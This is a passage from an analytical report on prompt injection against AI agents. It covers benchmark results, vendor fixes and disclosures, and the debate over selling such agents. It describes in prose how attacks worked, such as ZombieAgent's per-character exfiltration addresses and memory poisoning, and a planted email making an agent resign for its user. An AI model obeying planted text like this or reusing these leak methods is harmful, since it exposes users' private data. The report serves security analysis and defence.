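Anthropic's system card for Opus 5, a document about the model's abilities and safety, reports results on a newer version of the Gray Swan benchmark. This version has 28 scenarios and 1,130 attacks chosen because they worked across several models. An attacker had a 2.0 per cent chance of succeeding within 15 attempts against Opus 5, compared with 5.5 per cent against its predecessor, Opus 4.8, and 20.0 per cent against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. With a single attempt, the chances were 0.2, 0.5 and 3.1 per cent respectively.

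Anthropic's *System Card* for Claude Fable 5.1, published in September, used a refreshed benchmark with 37 scenarios and 1,804 attacks. Fable 5.1 had the lowest attack success rate, 1.0 per cent within 15 attempts. The rate for Opus 5 rose from 2.0 per cent in July to 4.8 per cent, although the model was the same. The new attacks probably account for most of the rise. The best model from another developer, Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash, had a rate of 9.2 per cent, and most of the others were between 24 and 53 per cent.

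Anthropic leaves out models that participants had attacked in the recent competitions, because attacks tailored to a model make it look worse than the rest. This makes the comparison fairer, but the remaining models faced only attacks written for other models, whereas a determined attacker would write one for the model the victim uses.

Both cards also report tests with Shade, Gray Swan's automated attacker, which improves through trial and error and gets 200 attempts per scenario. The table shows how much the result for one model, Opus 5, depends on the test. In every row, the model could reason before it answered.

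| Test of Opus 5 | Safeguards against injection | Attempts that succeeded | Scenarios broken |
|---|---|---|---|
| Coding, Shade, July | None | 0.56% | 13 of 40 |
| Coding, Shade, September | None | 2.68% | 27 of 40 |
| Coding, stronger Shade, September | None | 90.93% | 40 of 40 |
| Coding, stronger Shade, September | Probes | 18.21% | 40 of 40 |
| Computer use, Shade, September | None | 0.18% | 1 of 14 |
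| Browser, human testers' attacks, July | None | 3.70% | 11 of 129 |
| Browser, human testers' attacks, July | Auto mode | 0% | 0 of 129 |

The probes inspect what a tool returns and flag text that looks like a planted instruction. Auto mode combines them with a classifier that blocks potentially dangerous tool calls.

Gray Swan trained the stronger version of Shade for longer and on more varied attacks. Its training used the same 40 scenarios as the test, an advantage few real attackers would have, and Anthropic regards the result as a stress test rather than a forecast. But the low attack success rates with the first version were evidently due in good part to that attacker's limits. The first version was also not fully adaptive, because Gray Swan trained it against earlier Claude models and ran it unchanged on the new ones.

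The September card also shows why testing the model alone can mislead. Anthropic's products have a separate classifier that looks for dangerous hacking requests and hands them to an older model, Opus 4.8. The stronger Shade succeeded in 56.87 per cent of attempts on Fable 5.1, but every success came from a response by Opus 4.8, and none came from the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself. Those requests may have been easier to resist, because the classifier had already removed the ones that looked most like hacking. Still, the classifier, which was meant as a safeguard, had exposed users to a model that is easier to hijack. This handover probably also explains why the first Shade did better against Opus 5 in September than in July, since Opus 4.8 handled 57 per cent of the requests in the later test.

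### Why successes cluster

In the July browser test, attackers made ten attempts in each of the 129 scenarios, and 3.70 per cent of attempts on Opus 5 succeeded without safeguards. If every attempt had had the same independent chance of success, the share of scenarios broken at least once would have been about

1 − (1 − 0.037)¹⁰ ≈ 0.31

or 40 scenarios. The attackers actually broke 11, or 8.5 per cent. There were about 48 successes in those 11 scenarios, an average of more than four in ten attempts, and none in the other 118.

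If scenario *i* has a chance *pᵢ* of success per attempt, the expected share of scenarios broken within *k* attempts is the average of 1 − (1 − *pᵢ*)ᵏ. When the chances differ between scenarios and the attacker gets more than one attempt, this share is always lower than if every scenario had the average chance. The Gray Swan results for GPT-5.6 Sol fit this pattern. A 3.1 per cent chance per attempt would give 38 per cent within 15 independent attempts, but the measured figure was 20.0 per cent.

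Clustering can also change how models compare. In the same browser test, attacks on the smaller Claude Sonnet 5 succeeded in 0.93 per cent of attempts, but they succeeded at least once in nine scenarios. Opus 5 was four times as susceptible when measured by attempts, but only slightly more susceptible when measured by scenarios. The rate per attempt is more informative about an attacker who has one chance, while the rate per scenario is more informative about one who can keep trying.

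### A million hostile pages

At a success rate of 0.2 per cent, an agent that read a million hostile pages would follow the planted instructions on about 2,000 of them. An agent browsing at random would rarely meet that many hostile pages, because planted instructions are rare on the open web. But attackers can also send hostile text directly to their victims. Anthropic gives the example of one email sent to a thousand inboxes, which at this rate would hijack two agents on average.

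But an attacker with an account on the same product can test different versions of an email and send only one that works, so it may succeed more often than the average attempt. In the 11 browser scenarios where at least one attack succeeded, about 43 per cent of attempts did. At that rate, a planted instruction read a million times would hijack agents about 430,000 times, provided the agents had no extra safeguards and were doing much the same task as in the test.

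### Conditions the tests don't reproduce

Attackers in these tests have some advantages over real ones. Participants in Gray Swan's competition could read the conversation before writing the attack, and they knew which tool call they had to trigger. Someone attacking a company's agent usually doesn't know what the user has asked for or which tools the agent has, and repeated failures might attract attention. Dziemian and colleagues therefore describe their results as an upper bound on how vulnerable agents are within a single turn. That seems right for attackers with the same skill and persistence, but a better attacker can succeed much more often, as the two versions of Shade show.

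Auto mode stopped every attack on Opus 5 in the browser test. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection* takes its headline from that result, but notes that it holds only with auto mode on. Claude Cowork users who leave auto mode off still have the probes, but neither card gives a browser result for the probes alone. Even with no successful attacks in 129 scenarios, up to 2.3 per cent of the scenarios an agent might meet could still be breakable, at the 95 per cent confidence level, if those tested were a random sample.

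A bigger gap is that real attackers can adapt to the safeguards. Fable 5.1 also had no failures in 110 scenarios with auto mode on, but testers had developed those attacks against an older model, Opus 4.7, and Anthropic doesn't describe anyone revising them to get past auto mode. Radware's researchers, by contrast, revised ShadowLeak until it got past ChatGPT's defences.

A public bounty is a better test of this. Anthropic's earlier system cards reported one in which people attacked the newest model directly, but in July the company was still setting up the bounty for Opus 5. *Beam Model Technical Report* describes a three-week Gray Swan bounty, sponsored by several AI developers, for attacks on agent software in use.

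Developers also choose what to test and publish. VentureBeat compared three developers' disclosures in early 2026 and found that only one had published how attack success rises with repeated attempts, or results with safeguards on and off. Anthropic's cards include both, so the most detailed evidence about Claude's resistance comes from its own developer. The browser test is Anthropic's own. Gray Swan ran the others, but developers help fund its competitions and receive the successful attacks on their own models. Those attacks help developers fix weaknesses, but may also make later models perform better on similar attacks than on new ones.

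Outside testers also make mistakes. Gray Swan found that the models had been able to reason before answering in some runs labelled "without thinking". In July, Anthropic reported a rate of 0.39 per cent for Opus 5 in computer-use tests without thinking. The September figure, with the setting corrected, was 3.57 per cent, but those tests also included the handover to older models.

Developers release new models so quickly that test results soon apply only to an older one. By 11 November, Mowshowitz was already reviewing the system card for Fable 5.1's successor in *Fable and Mythos 5.2* (2026).

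### Tampering with the task

Most benchmarks test whether planted text can make an agent do something the user didn't ask for. An attacker may gain as much by changing how the agent carries out the user's request. Zhang, Bertran and colleagues (2026) call this task tampering in *Beyond Instruction Override*.

In one example, a user asks an agent to settle a dispute over a damaged item and to base the refund on the shop's order record, which authorises $899.99. The buyer's evidence contains a false claim that would raise the refund to $1,074.99. If the agent relies on the claim, it still uses the right tool to settle the dispute but refunds $175 too much.

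Zhang and colleagues define injection more broadly than a definition that requires a planted instruction. A buyer who wants a larger refund could tell the agent to pay the higher amount, invent a rule about repair costs, or warn that a smaller refund will lead to a chargeback. The buyer could also claim that the system can't process a smaller refund, say that the displayed amount leaves something out, or give a false authorised total. Only the first of these has to be an order, but all six count as injections because the buyer has no authority to set the refund. If the user had asked only why the buyer wanted a refund, a false answer would be misinformation, since the buyer is the right source for that. The definition would also cover the false note on a résumé saying that the applicant has been approved.

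The researchers built 90 such cases, set in a company's office, an open-source software project and an online marketplace. In each case they kept the task and the harmful result the same and varied only the attacker's justification. The attackers knew what someone in their role would know, but not the user's exact request, which is more realistic than in Gray Swan's competition. But the researchers paired every attack with a task it could affect, so their rates don't include times when a planted claim would have been irrelevant.

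Across five models, the attacks succeeded 17.0 per cent of the time without a defence. False claims about rules, available actions or the current state worked better on average than stating the attacker's goal outright. A defence that finds and removes planted instructions cut the success rate of attacks that stated the goal to 2.4 per cent. With the same defence, false interpretations of what the agent had observed still succeeded 9.5 per cent of the time, and false claims about the current state 12.1 per cent. A benchmark containing only attacks that state the goal would have greatly overstated the defence's effectiveness.

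Another defence, which checks each tool call against a policy generated for the task, reduced the overall rate only to 15.4 per cent. The five models, which included Claude Sonnet 4.5 and DeepSeek V3.1, were older than Opus 5, so newer models may do better. But a stronger model wouldn't fix the policy. An agent settling refunds needs permission to issue refunds, and a policy that allows them without checking the order record will allow a refund of $1,074.99.

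## How vendors respond and what counts as a fix

A vendor that says it has fixed a prompt injection flaw may have blocked the reported form of attack, closed the channel through which data leaked, limited what the agent can do, or trained the model to be less likely to obey planted instructions. Vendors often combine these fixes and seldom say which they used, even though each leaves an attacker different options.

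### Blocking the reported attack

The narrowest fix stops only the exact attack that was reported. In October 2025, Zenity Labs told Perplexity that a calendar invitation could make the Comet browser read files on the user's computer and send them to an attacker. According to Particle News' *Zenity Labs details PleaseFix flaws in agentic browsers*, Perplexity released a fix on 23 January 2026, but writing the files' addresses in another form bypassed it. A second update on 13 February restricted access to local files. Zenity (2026) announced the flaws on 3 March.

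An attacker can phrase a planted instruction in endless ways, whereas a file's address can be written in only a limited number. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) argues that this is why filters on incoming text usually miss well-developed attacks. Such attacks read like ordinary office mail, so detecting them is close to detecting a lie, often without the context needed to do so.

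### How ZombieAgent got past the ShadowLeak fix

Blocking a channel that leaks data works whatever the planted text says, but the model may still obey the text, and the attacker can look for another channel. The ShadowLeak attack made ChatGPT's Deep Research write private details into a web address and open it. OpenAI responded by stopping ChatGPT from altering addresses. Radware's *ZombieAgent* explains that ChatGPT would then open an address only exactly as received, even when told to add something to it.

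Zvika Babo, one of the researchers behind ShadowLeak, got around OpenAI's rule in September 2025 by supplying every address in advance. His planted email listed one address on the attacker's server for each letter and digit, and one for a space. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something in Gmail, it read the email, found a private detail in the mailbox and spelled it out by opening the matching addresses one after another, without changing any of them. The rule didn't prevent this because it covered what the model wrote into an address, and here, as in CamoLeak, the information was in the model's choice of addresses.

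To preserve the order, Babo prepared a separate address for each character in each position. A block of ten characters needs 260 addresses for letters and 100 for digits, which a short program can generate.

OpenAI had also tried to keep ChatGPT's memory separate from outside data. After ChatGPT used a connector in a chat, it couldn't use its memory in that chat. It also couldn't open an attacker's address stored in memory. But it could still read its memory first and then use a connector. Babo wrote a file that made ChatGPT save two rules to memory when a user shared the file with it. Under the first rule, ChatGPT would read a certain email from the attacker and follow its instructions whenever the user wrote a message. Under the second, it would save any sensitive information the user mentioned. The attacker's addresses could stay in the email, so the ban on opening addresses from memory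 didn't stop the attack. From then on, ChatGPT leaked data before answering each message, even in new chats.

Babo also altered a medical history in ChatGPT's memory, which led to harmful advice. Another version of the attack collected email addresses from the inbox and sent them to the attacker's server, which mailed the planted text to each address. Morris II, by contrast, needed the victim's assistant to send the infected messages.

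Babo reported all this through Bugcrowd on 26 September 2025. Bugcrowd reproduced the attack four days later and passed it on. OpenAI fixed it on 16 December, 81 days after the report. Radware (2026) announced ZombieAgent on 8 January without describing the fix. The same month, OpenAI published a description of its check, which lets ChatGPT automatically fetch only addresses that OpenAI's crawler has already recorded. Embrace The Red dates the stricter checking to around August 2025, before Babo's attack worked. Perhaps the check didn't yet cover the route he used, the kind of gap Rehberger worried about.

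The check also leaves some decisions to users, because useful links can carry personal information. In an example from OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links*, a link to a car search reveals to the search company that the user lives in London. ChatGPT asks the user to approve certain links, including every link to a site whose owner has asked OpenAI not to catalogue it.

### Limiting what a hijacked agent can do

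OpenAI compares an agent to a customer service worker who can issue refunds. Some customers will lie, so the employer's software caps refunds instead of relying on the worker to spot every lie. A similar limit on an agent still holds when an attacker has fooled the model.

Perplexity's February update restricted Comet's access to files, but that would not stop another attack Zenity had shown, in which Comet changed settings and extracted secrets through the password manager 1Password when the user had left it unlocked. The attack needed no flaw in 1Password and no access to local files.

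Deciding where to set the limit is also hard. SOPGuard, a defence proposed by Wang and colleagues, asks the user before an agent moves data from one website to another. *SPIDES* (2026), which proposes a rival defence, describes a test in which a private message on a social network contained an instruction to copy the user's recovery email address into their public profile. Because the data stayed on the same site, SOPGuard did not ask the user, and the leak succeeded in all 25 runs. The rival defence blocked the change to the profile because the instruction came from an untrusted message. SOPGuard can also ask for approval when the user's task plainly requires the transfer, such as copying a product's name from one site to another.

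Claude's auto mode, which blocks potentially dangerous tool calls, stopped all 720 attacks in one of Anthropic's evaluations. Willison wants independent confirmation of this result. He doubts that any version of auto mode could catch a software package whose instructions include a normal-looking setup step that runs a program built to steal data.

### OpenAI's automated attacker

Vendors also train models to resist prompt injection. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (22 December 2025) describes how the company did this for its browser agent. OpenAI trained a language model to attack the agent through reinforcement learning, in which a model tries different actions and training strengthens those that succeed. It chose this method partly because a harmful task may take many steps, and the outcome is known only at the end.

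The attacker model can send a draft attack to a simulator, which runs the agent as if it had come across the planted text and returns a full record of the agent's reasoning and actions. The model can revise and retest the draft several times before producing a final version. Outsiders don't see the agent's full reasoning, so OpenAI hopes to find attacks before they do.

In OpenAI's main example, the attacker put an email in the user's inbox with instructions to send a resignation letter to the chief executive. When the user later asked the agent to write an out-of-office reply, the agent read the email, treated the instructions as authoritative, and resigned on the user's behalf instead of writing the reply. Other attacks led the agent through tens or hundreds of steps, and some used strategies that neither OpenAI's human testers nor outside researchers had reported.

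OpenAI then trained the agent to resist the attacks that were succeeding and released the new version to all Atlas users. It also used records of the attacks to improve monitoring and other safeguards around the model. It published no success rates from before and after, so the size of the improvement is unknown. The company wrote that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". It still advised users to keep the agent logged out where possible and to avoid broad requests, such as telling it to deal with their email however it sees fit.

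Training an agent against known attacks makes those and similar attacks less likely to work, but doesn't guarantee that it will resist others. Roesner and Kohlbrenner carried out their attack on Atlas in early 2026, after OpenAI released the retrained agent.

### Eight disclosures compared

The dates in the table come from the researchers' accounts, except those for Comet, which come from Particle News. A CVE number identifies a flaw in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities. "None given" means the accounts used here mention no CVE number.

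| Case | Reported | Repaired | Kind of fix | CVE number | Evaded later |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Picture leak in ChatGPT | April 2023 | December 2023, in part | Leak channel | None given | Yes, in several ways |
| EchoLeak | January 2025 | May 2025 | Not described | CVE-2025-32711 | Later attacks on Copilot used other routes |
| Calendar invitations to Gemini | 22 February 2025 | By August 2025 | Limits on actions, and filters | None given | Yes, by SafeBreach |
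| ShadowLeak | 18 June 2025 | Early August 2025 | Leak channel | None given | Yes, by ZombieAgent |
| HashJack in Edge | 20 August 2025 | 27 October 2025 | Not described | None given | No report of it |
| ZombieAgent | 26 September 2025 | 16 December 2025 | Not described | None given | No report of it |
| File theft through Comet | 22 October 2025 | 23 January and 13 February 2026 | Reported form, then limits on access | None given | First fix only |
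| Gemini panel in Chrome | Not given | Early January 2026 | Ordinary code repair | CVE-2026-0628 | No report of it |

Researchers evaded at least one fix in four of the eight cases. This proportion can't be generalized to all fixes, because these cases are well known and researchers who fail to evade a fix have little to publish.

The two flaws with CVE numbers, the Chrome flaw and EchoLeak, are of different kinds. The Chrome flaw was a conventional error that let an extension gain privileges it should not have had, as KBI.Media's *Palo Alto Networks Unit 42 Uncovers Vulnerability in Google Chrome’s Gemini* (2026) explains. A CVE number suits such a flaw because an administrator can look up which versions of Chrome need replacing. It is less useful for a service that runs on the vendor's computers, where customers have nothing to install, though Microsoft still gave EchoLeak one. The lack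 of a CVE number is therefore poor evidence that a flaw was minor. ShadowLeak seems never to have had one, although it could steal private mail.

### Repairs that outsiders cannot check

A fix on the vendor's servers protects all users at once, including those who never install updates. But outsiders usually can't access the old version to compare it with the new one. OpenAI fixed ShadowLeak without notifying Radware and marked the flaw as resolved only about a month later. When an attack stops working, a researcher may not be able to tell whether the vendor blocked its wording, closed the channel or changed the model. If the model's behavior varies from run to run, a few failed attempts don't even show that anything has changed.

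This also makes disagreements hard to settle. In March 2026, OpenAI reprinted much of the ShadowLeak email and wrote that it had worked 50 per cent of the time in testing, whereas Radware had reported 100 per cent. The two companies may have tested different versions, since Radware had several that worked. Nobody outside OpenAI can now repeat the test on the system as it was.

Public advisories go out of date when vendors fix flaws without announcing it. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT “Command Memories” Injection via SearchGPT* lists a flaw involving ChatGPT's memory as unpatched, but a reader can't tell from the advisory alone whether OpenAI has since repaired it.

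### Reports that vendors decline

Researchers report many flaws through bug bounties, programmes that pay for reports meeting certain rules. Those rules define what counts as a flaw, and vendors apply them differently to prompt injection. Roesner and Kohlbrenner gave seven vendors more than 60 days' notice of their findings about agentic browsers. Brave, Google and Microsoft sent thoughtful replies. OpenAI declined the report because it contained no complete prompt injection attack. Anthropic, Firefox and Perplexity had not replied when the paper came out, but the University of Washington later reported that Perplexity had also declined the report.

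Requiring a complete attack helps keep the number of reports manageable, because anyone can argue that an agent might obey a planted instruction. But Roesner and Kohlbrenner were studying what an agent can reach once any injection succeeds. Requiring a working injection also encourages vendors to block its wording, which they can do without changing what the agent can reach.

Google's classification of HashJack depended on which programme received the report. Simonovich reported the flaw to Chrome's bounty programme on 23 August 2025, and an engineer reproduced it two days later. The programme rated it as low severity and did not treat it as a vulnerability. At Google's direction, Simonovich filed it again with the programme for abuse of Google's products, which marked it as intended behaviour. Google had also classed the use of invisible characters against Gemini as social engineering. Android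 Authority's *Google says it won't fix Gemini security flaw* (2025) points out that this puts the responsibility on the user.

Zenity got similarly mixed answers about the browser attacks it presented in August 2026. Calcalist reports that some companies issued fixes and others said the products were working as intended. In *PleaseFix*, Zenity co-founder Bargury (2026) also calls the underlying features "design choices, not vulnerabilities". A vendor can use that description to close a report, but Bargury means that no patch for a single bug will be enough and the design itself has to change.

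Some vendors don't give a reason. LayerX lists its BioShocking report to Perplexity as "Closed / ignored" and says that Fellou, Genspark and Sigma never responded. The vendors affected by Trail of Bits' browser findings declined its offer to coordinate publication. Trail of Bits then published the attacks without naming the products, so users of agentic browsers can't tell from the article whether theirs was affected.

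## Whether such agents should be on the market

Companies are selling agents that they admit strangers can sometimes hijack. Critics object to this for several reasons, which combine into one argument:

1. Language models cannot reliably separate instructions from data.
2. Useful agents combine private data, untrusted content and a way to communicate outward, Willison's lethal trifecta.
3. Users can neither judge nor control the resulting risk.
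4. Releasing such agents to the general public is therefore irresponsible.

### Can models separate instructions from data?

Hardly anyone claims that current models can do this reliably. OpenAI wrote in December 2025 that prompt injection, like scams, was unlikely ever to be fully solved. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) calls it a "fundamental, unsolved weakness" of all large language models.

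David C of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre fears that prompt injection will cause a wave of breaches like the one SQL injection caused, as companies build models into most of their software. SQL injection break-ins went on for about a decade before websites had safer defaults, even though that flaw has a complete remedy, which prompt injection lacks. He doesn't call for a ban, but he advises that a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk may be a poor use for a language model.

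However, the software around an agent's model can also limit the damage. Trail of Bits blames the browser attacks it found on inadequate isolation, which engineers can improve without a better model. Such limits can have gaps, and Willison describes one in the tool Claude uses to open web pages. The tool restricted Claude to addresses the user had typed, addresses a search had returned, and links on pages it had already opened. A researcher, Ayush Paul, built a site that used those links to make Claude spell out the user's name, home city and employer letter by letter. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links on fetched pages. This fix works no matter how persuasive a page is, but it makes the tool less useful for browsing.

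### Does a useful agent need all three?

Meta's Rule of Two applies until researchers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injections. It allows an agent no more than two of these properties within a session:

- **A:** it can process untrustworthy input.
- **B:** it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change things or communicate externally.

Property C is broader than outward communication, so the rule also covers agents that delete files or spend money.

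Meta's main example is an email assistant that receives a spam message containing instructions to forward the user's inbox. Removing any one property stops the attack. The assistant could read mail only from trusted senders, work in a test environment without real data, or send messages only to trusted recipients or after a person has checked the draft. An agent can also change properties partway through a session, for instance by searching the web first and then losing its ability to communicate before it opens internal systems.

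An agent can be useful without all three properties in Meta's rule. But many people want an email assistant that has all three, one that reads strangers' messages, searches old mail and sends replies. An assistant that ignored strangers would miss a new customer's enquiry. Meta permits all three together only under supervision, such as human approval, and admits that the rule is a poor fit for some uses people want, including jobs that run in the background. The safety of products with all three properties depends heavily on how well people supervise them.

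Following the rule doesn't make an assistant harmless either. Meta excludes "lower consequence" results such as misinformation in an answer, but the false account warning in Gemini's email summary could have led someone to give away their password.

### Can users control the risk?

OpenAI advises Atlas users to check every confirmation request carefully. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users of its coding agent approve 97 per cent of permission prompts. Most of those prompts are probably safe, so the figure alone doesn't show that users are careless.

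Anthropic therefore commissioned an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through a coding session, one prompt showed a clearly dangerous command instead of the real one. 143 testers, or 13.6 per cent, refused it. About 17 per cent refused when it came early in the session, but only about 5 per cent did after 50 or more prompts. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they may have been less careful than usual. Claude Code users reject 39 per cent of the plans Claude asks them to approve, which suggests they read some requests closely.

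Software may supervise agents better than people do. Anthropic's auto mode blocked 89 per cent of the same commands. It let through only six that a tester had refused, so adding the human check would have raised the share blocked by about half a percentage point. Anthropic made auto mode the default for new Claude Code sessions on most subscription plans in August 2026 and announced the same change for most Claude apps in October.

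This experiment tested dangerous commands, not planted instructions. All 720 attacks failed in the separate injection test, but the testers had developed them against an older model. In late August, Rehberger reported an attack that he says got past auto mode 80 per cent of the time, though it misled the agent about its environment and contained no instruction for the model to follow. Willison accepts that auto mode is better than asking people to approve everything, but he would rather keep coding agents in an isolated environment with limited network access and no access to passwords.

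With automatic checks, users need to do less to control the risk, but they still can't judge it. Someone who relies on auto mode has to trust Anthropic's account of how well it works. Few drivers can assess their own brakes either, but governments set standards for brakes. In *OpenAI says prompt injections that can trick AI browsers like ChatGPT Atlas* (Nolan, 2025), Charlie Eriksen of Aikido Security said it was reasonable to doubt whether the trade-off made sense for everyday users. He wanted much clearer limits on what agents may do and whose instructions they should follow.

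### The comparison with people who get phished

Perhaps people should accept fallible agents, since employers already give staff access to email and bank accounts even though some of them will fall for phishing. *Piloting Claude for Chrome* (Willison, 2025) quotes a similar comparison from Anthropic's announcement of Claude for Chrome. OpenAI hopes that people will eventually be able to trust its agent as they would a "highly competent, security-aware colleague".

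David Kohlbrenner, one of the researchers who compared seven agentic browsers, told the University of Washington that agents still fall for attacks that wouldn't work on people.

Copies of an agent also share their weaknesses. If an attacker sends an email to 1,000 employees, each with an independent 1 per cent chance of being fooled, it will fool about ten of them. If the recipients are instead 1,000 identical agents, and one email in 100 fools all of them while the rest fool none, the average is still ten, but the attacker can test emails on their own copy of the agent and send only the one that works. Real agents vary more than this because their tasks differ and their answers are partly random. Still, a company whose staff all use the same agent may have no sceptical colleague to warn the others. Shared weaknesses also help defenders, since one update can protect every copy, whereas 1,000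 employees all need training.

An agent's speed makes its mistakes harder to catch. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) describes an agent that processes invoices and finds that a document-signing subscription is about to lapse. An employee would recognise that renewal means a new contract and ask someone, and conventional software would stop, but the agent might try to pay because renewal seems to help with its task. The example involves no attacker, but a planted instruction could exploit the same tendency, and an agent could make many payments before anyone looked.

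An employer can also discipline an employee who breaks the rules, but it can't discipline an agent. OpenAI says the person or organisation deploying an agent remains responsible for the outcome. A company can prepare for that responsibility with spending limits and audit logs, but someone who installs an agentic browser at home usually can't.

The comparison with human workers is a weaker argument for release than it seems, because employers also limit what a deceived worker can do, as with the capped refunds in OpenAI's customer service example. The comparison supports releasing agents with similar limits, but not giving one agent access to all of a user's accounts.

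### What lower success rates changed

When it released Opus 4.5 in November 2025, Anthropic reported that about 1 per cent of attacks on its browser agent succeeded. Anthropic's *Mitigating the risk of prompt injections in browser use* says that this "still represents meaningful risk". The company nevertheless opened Claude for Chrome to everyone on its Max plan, citing its progress. The Decoder reported that, by July 2026, no attack on Opus 5 succeeded in Anthropic's browser test with auto mode on.

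Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, wrote that preventing prompt injection was still impossible in general, but that developers were getting much better at blocking specific cases. A commenter objected that other architectures might solve the general problem. That is possible, but the agents now on sale use current architectures.

Willison has become somewhat more optimistic. In August 2025 he expected the whole idea of an agentic browser extension to prove "fatally flawed". That December he successfully used Claude's extension to find a setting on a website he managed, though he watched it closely and remained sceptical. In June 2026 he wrote about a public challenge to steal secrets from an assistant running Opus 4.6 by sending it email. All of the roughly 6,000 attempts failed. Willison took this as a sign that training was helping, but he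 still advised against using such models where an injection could do irreversible damage, because a more sophisticated attacker might succeed.

A low average rate is less reassuring when attackers can persist and choose their moment. At the 0.2 per cent per attempt measured for Opus 5 on one benchmark, an attacker who sent one email a day for a year would have a chance of

1 − (1 − 0.002)³⁶⁵ ≈ 0.52

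of succeeding at least once, if the attempts were independent. Because successes cluster in certain tasks, the chance would be lower against many agents and much higher against some. An attacker who finds a working instruction can also save it for the week when a company pays its largest invoices. A success rate counts that attack the same as one on a quiet day.

Whether a low success rate is acceptable therefore depends on how much harm one successful attack can do. OpenAI's August guide suggests looking at the "maximum completed effect", the most consequential outcome an agent can produce before another person or system makes an independent decision. A rate of 0.2 per cent may be acceptable for an agent that drafts replies, but not for one that can transfer a company's savings on its own.

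So far, no widely known disaster has forced vendors to be more cautious. Rehberger calls the result a "normalization of deviance", the sociologist Diane Vaughan's term for what happens when organisations get away with breaking safety rules and then relax further. This pattern partly explains the loss of the space shuttle Challenger. Willison predicted a comparable disaster for coding agents in 2026, and in May he noted that it had not yet happened.

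At least one smaller incident indicates that attackers are willing to exploit prompt injection flaws. Cline, a coding tool, used an AI agent to sort bug reports, and the researcher Adnan Khan showed that the title of a report could hijack the agent. According to Willison, Cline didn't deal with Khan's warning promptly, and an anonymous attacker published a tampered release of the tool. The release installed another agent, OpenClaw, but did nothing more dangerous.

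### What restrictions cost

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode removes most of the ways data can leave ChatGPT. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* explains that browsing in this mode uses only stored copies of pages, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network. Software enforces this regardless of what the model writes. The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* reports that users also lose agent mode and Deep Research, and that OpenAI warns of remaining risks from connected apps and newly discovered techniques.

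OpenAI began offering the mode to personal accounts in June 2026, including free ones, but says most users don't need it. OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, recommends it for people at higher risk because of who they are or what they work on. Willison welcomed the mode but pointed out that its existence implies ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect against determined data thieves. Ordinary users may need more protection than Stuckey's advice suggests, because an attacker can send the same email to thousands of people without knowing who they are.

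| Choice | What the user gives up | Risk that remains |
|---|---|---|
| Logged-out browsing | Any task that needs the user's accounts | False answers, and leaks of what the user tells the agent |
| Lockdown Mode | Live browsing, agent mode and Deep Research | False answers, and leaks through connected apps |
| Mail from trusted senders only | Help with messages from strangers | Attacks from a trusted sender's hijacked account |
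| Approval of every action | Work that runs unattended | Approvals given without reading |
| Narrow tasks | Handing over a whole job, such as managing an inbox | Planted instructions that the agent meets during the task |
| Staged release | Early access for most people | The same attacks on those who have access |

Making narrow requests is little trouble for the user, but it offers limited protection. In OpenAI's demonstration, the user asked only for an out-of-office reply, but the agent sent a resignation letter.

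Anthropic released Claude for Chrome in stages, starting with 1,000 Max subscribers in August 2025, according to eWeek's *Claude-for-Chrome Pilot* (2025), and reaching all paid plans on 18 December, according to Zenity Labs' *Claude in Chrome*. A pilot gives developers time to fix problems while few people are exposed. But 1,000 users are also a small target for criminals, so an uneventful pilot is weak evidence of what will happen after general release.

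### Should vendors sell them to everyone?

In December 2025, Gartner, a technology advisory firm, recommended that companies block all AI browsers "in the foreseeable future", according to TechNewsWorld's *Gartner Recommends Avoiding AI Browsers*. Infosecurity Magazine's *Gartner Calls For Pause on AI Browser Use* reports that, besides prompt injection, Gartner worried that agents would book the wrong flights, send company data to outside AI services, or complete employees' security training for them.

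Javvad Malik of the security training company KnowBe4 replied that blanket bans rarely last and that companies should assess the particular AI service behind each browser. A ban would also be hard to define. According to Thurrott's *Gartner*, Gartner identifies an AI browser by two features, one of which is a sidebar that can summarise the page in a tab. The assistants in mainstream browsers such as Edge and Chrome can now do this too. A company could turn off the agent and keep the browser, but private users have no security department to decide this for them.

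Kohlbrenner says browser agents "aren't ready for the public" and that even fairly knowledgeable people shouldn't trust one with access to their email or bank account. His colleague Franziska Roesner attributes the rapid releases to competitive pressure. They studied browsers from early 2026, and Gartner, Meta and David C took their positions in late 2025, before the Opus 5 results. Those results weaken the case against the best-protected products, but they don't show that other vendors' agents are equally safe.

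Anthropic defends auto mode partly on the grounds that a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start with permission checks switched off, so for many users the alternative to automatic checks is no checks at all. This is a good reason to prefer auto mode to constant approval, but a weaker reason to release an agent in the first place, because someone without an agent has no permission checks to switch off. Anthropic also says that auto mode doesn't eliminate risk, and still recommends that people review high-stakes changes themselves.

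The argument against general release is therefore strongest for agents that can use all of a person's accounts and take irreversible actions without an independent check. It is much weaker for a tool that summarises one page, or for an agent that browses without logins. Vendors could sell the more powerful agents with restrictions on by default and let users lift them one at a time. Lockdown Mode is off by default, so users have to know about the risk before they think of turning it on.

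## What the law says about planting instructions and about hijacked agents

Courts have decided very little about whether planting an instruction is a crime, or whether the victim can get compensation from the planter, a bank or the vendor. There is no publicly reported prosecution for an indirect prompt injection, and the known judgments punish people who hid instructions in court filings. For other cases, lawyers have to apply laws written for different problems.

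### Who accesses a website when an agent clicks

The main American hacking law, the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act (CFAA), makes it an offence to obtain information by intentionally accessing a computer without authorisation or beyond it. The leading case on how this applies to AI agents, Amazon v. Perplexity, did not involve injection.

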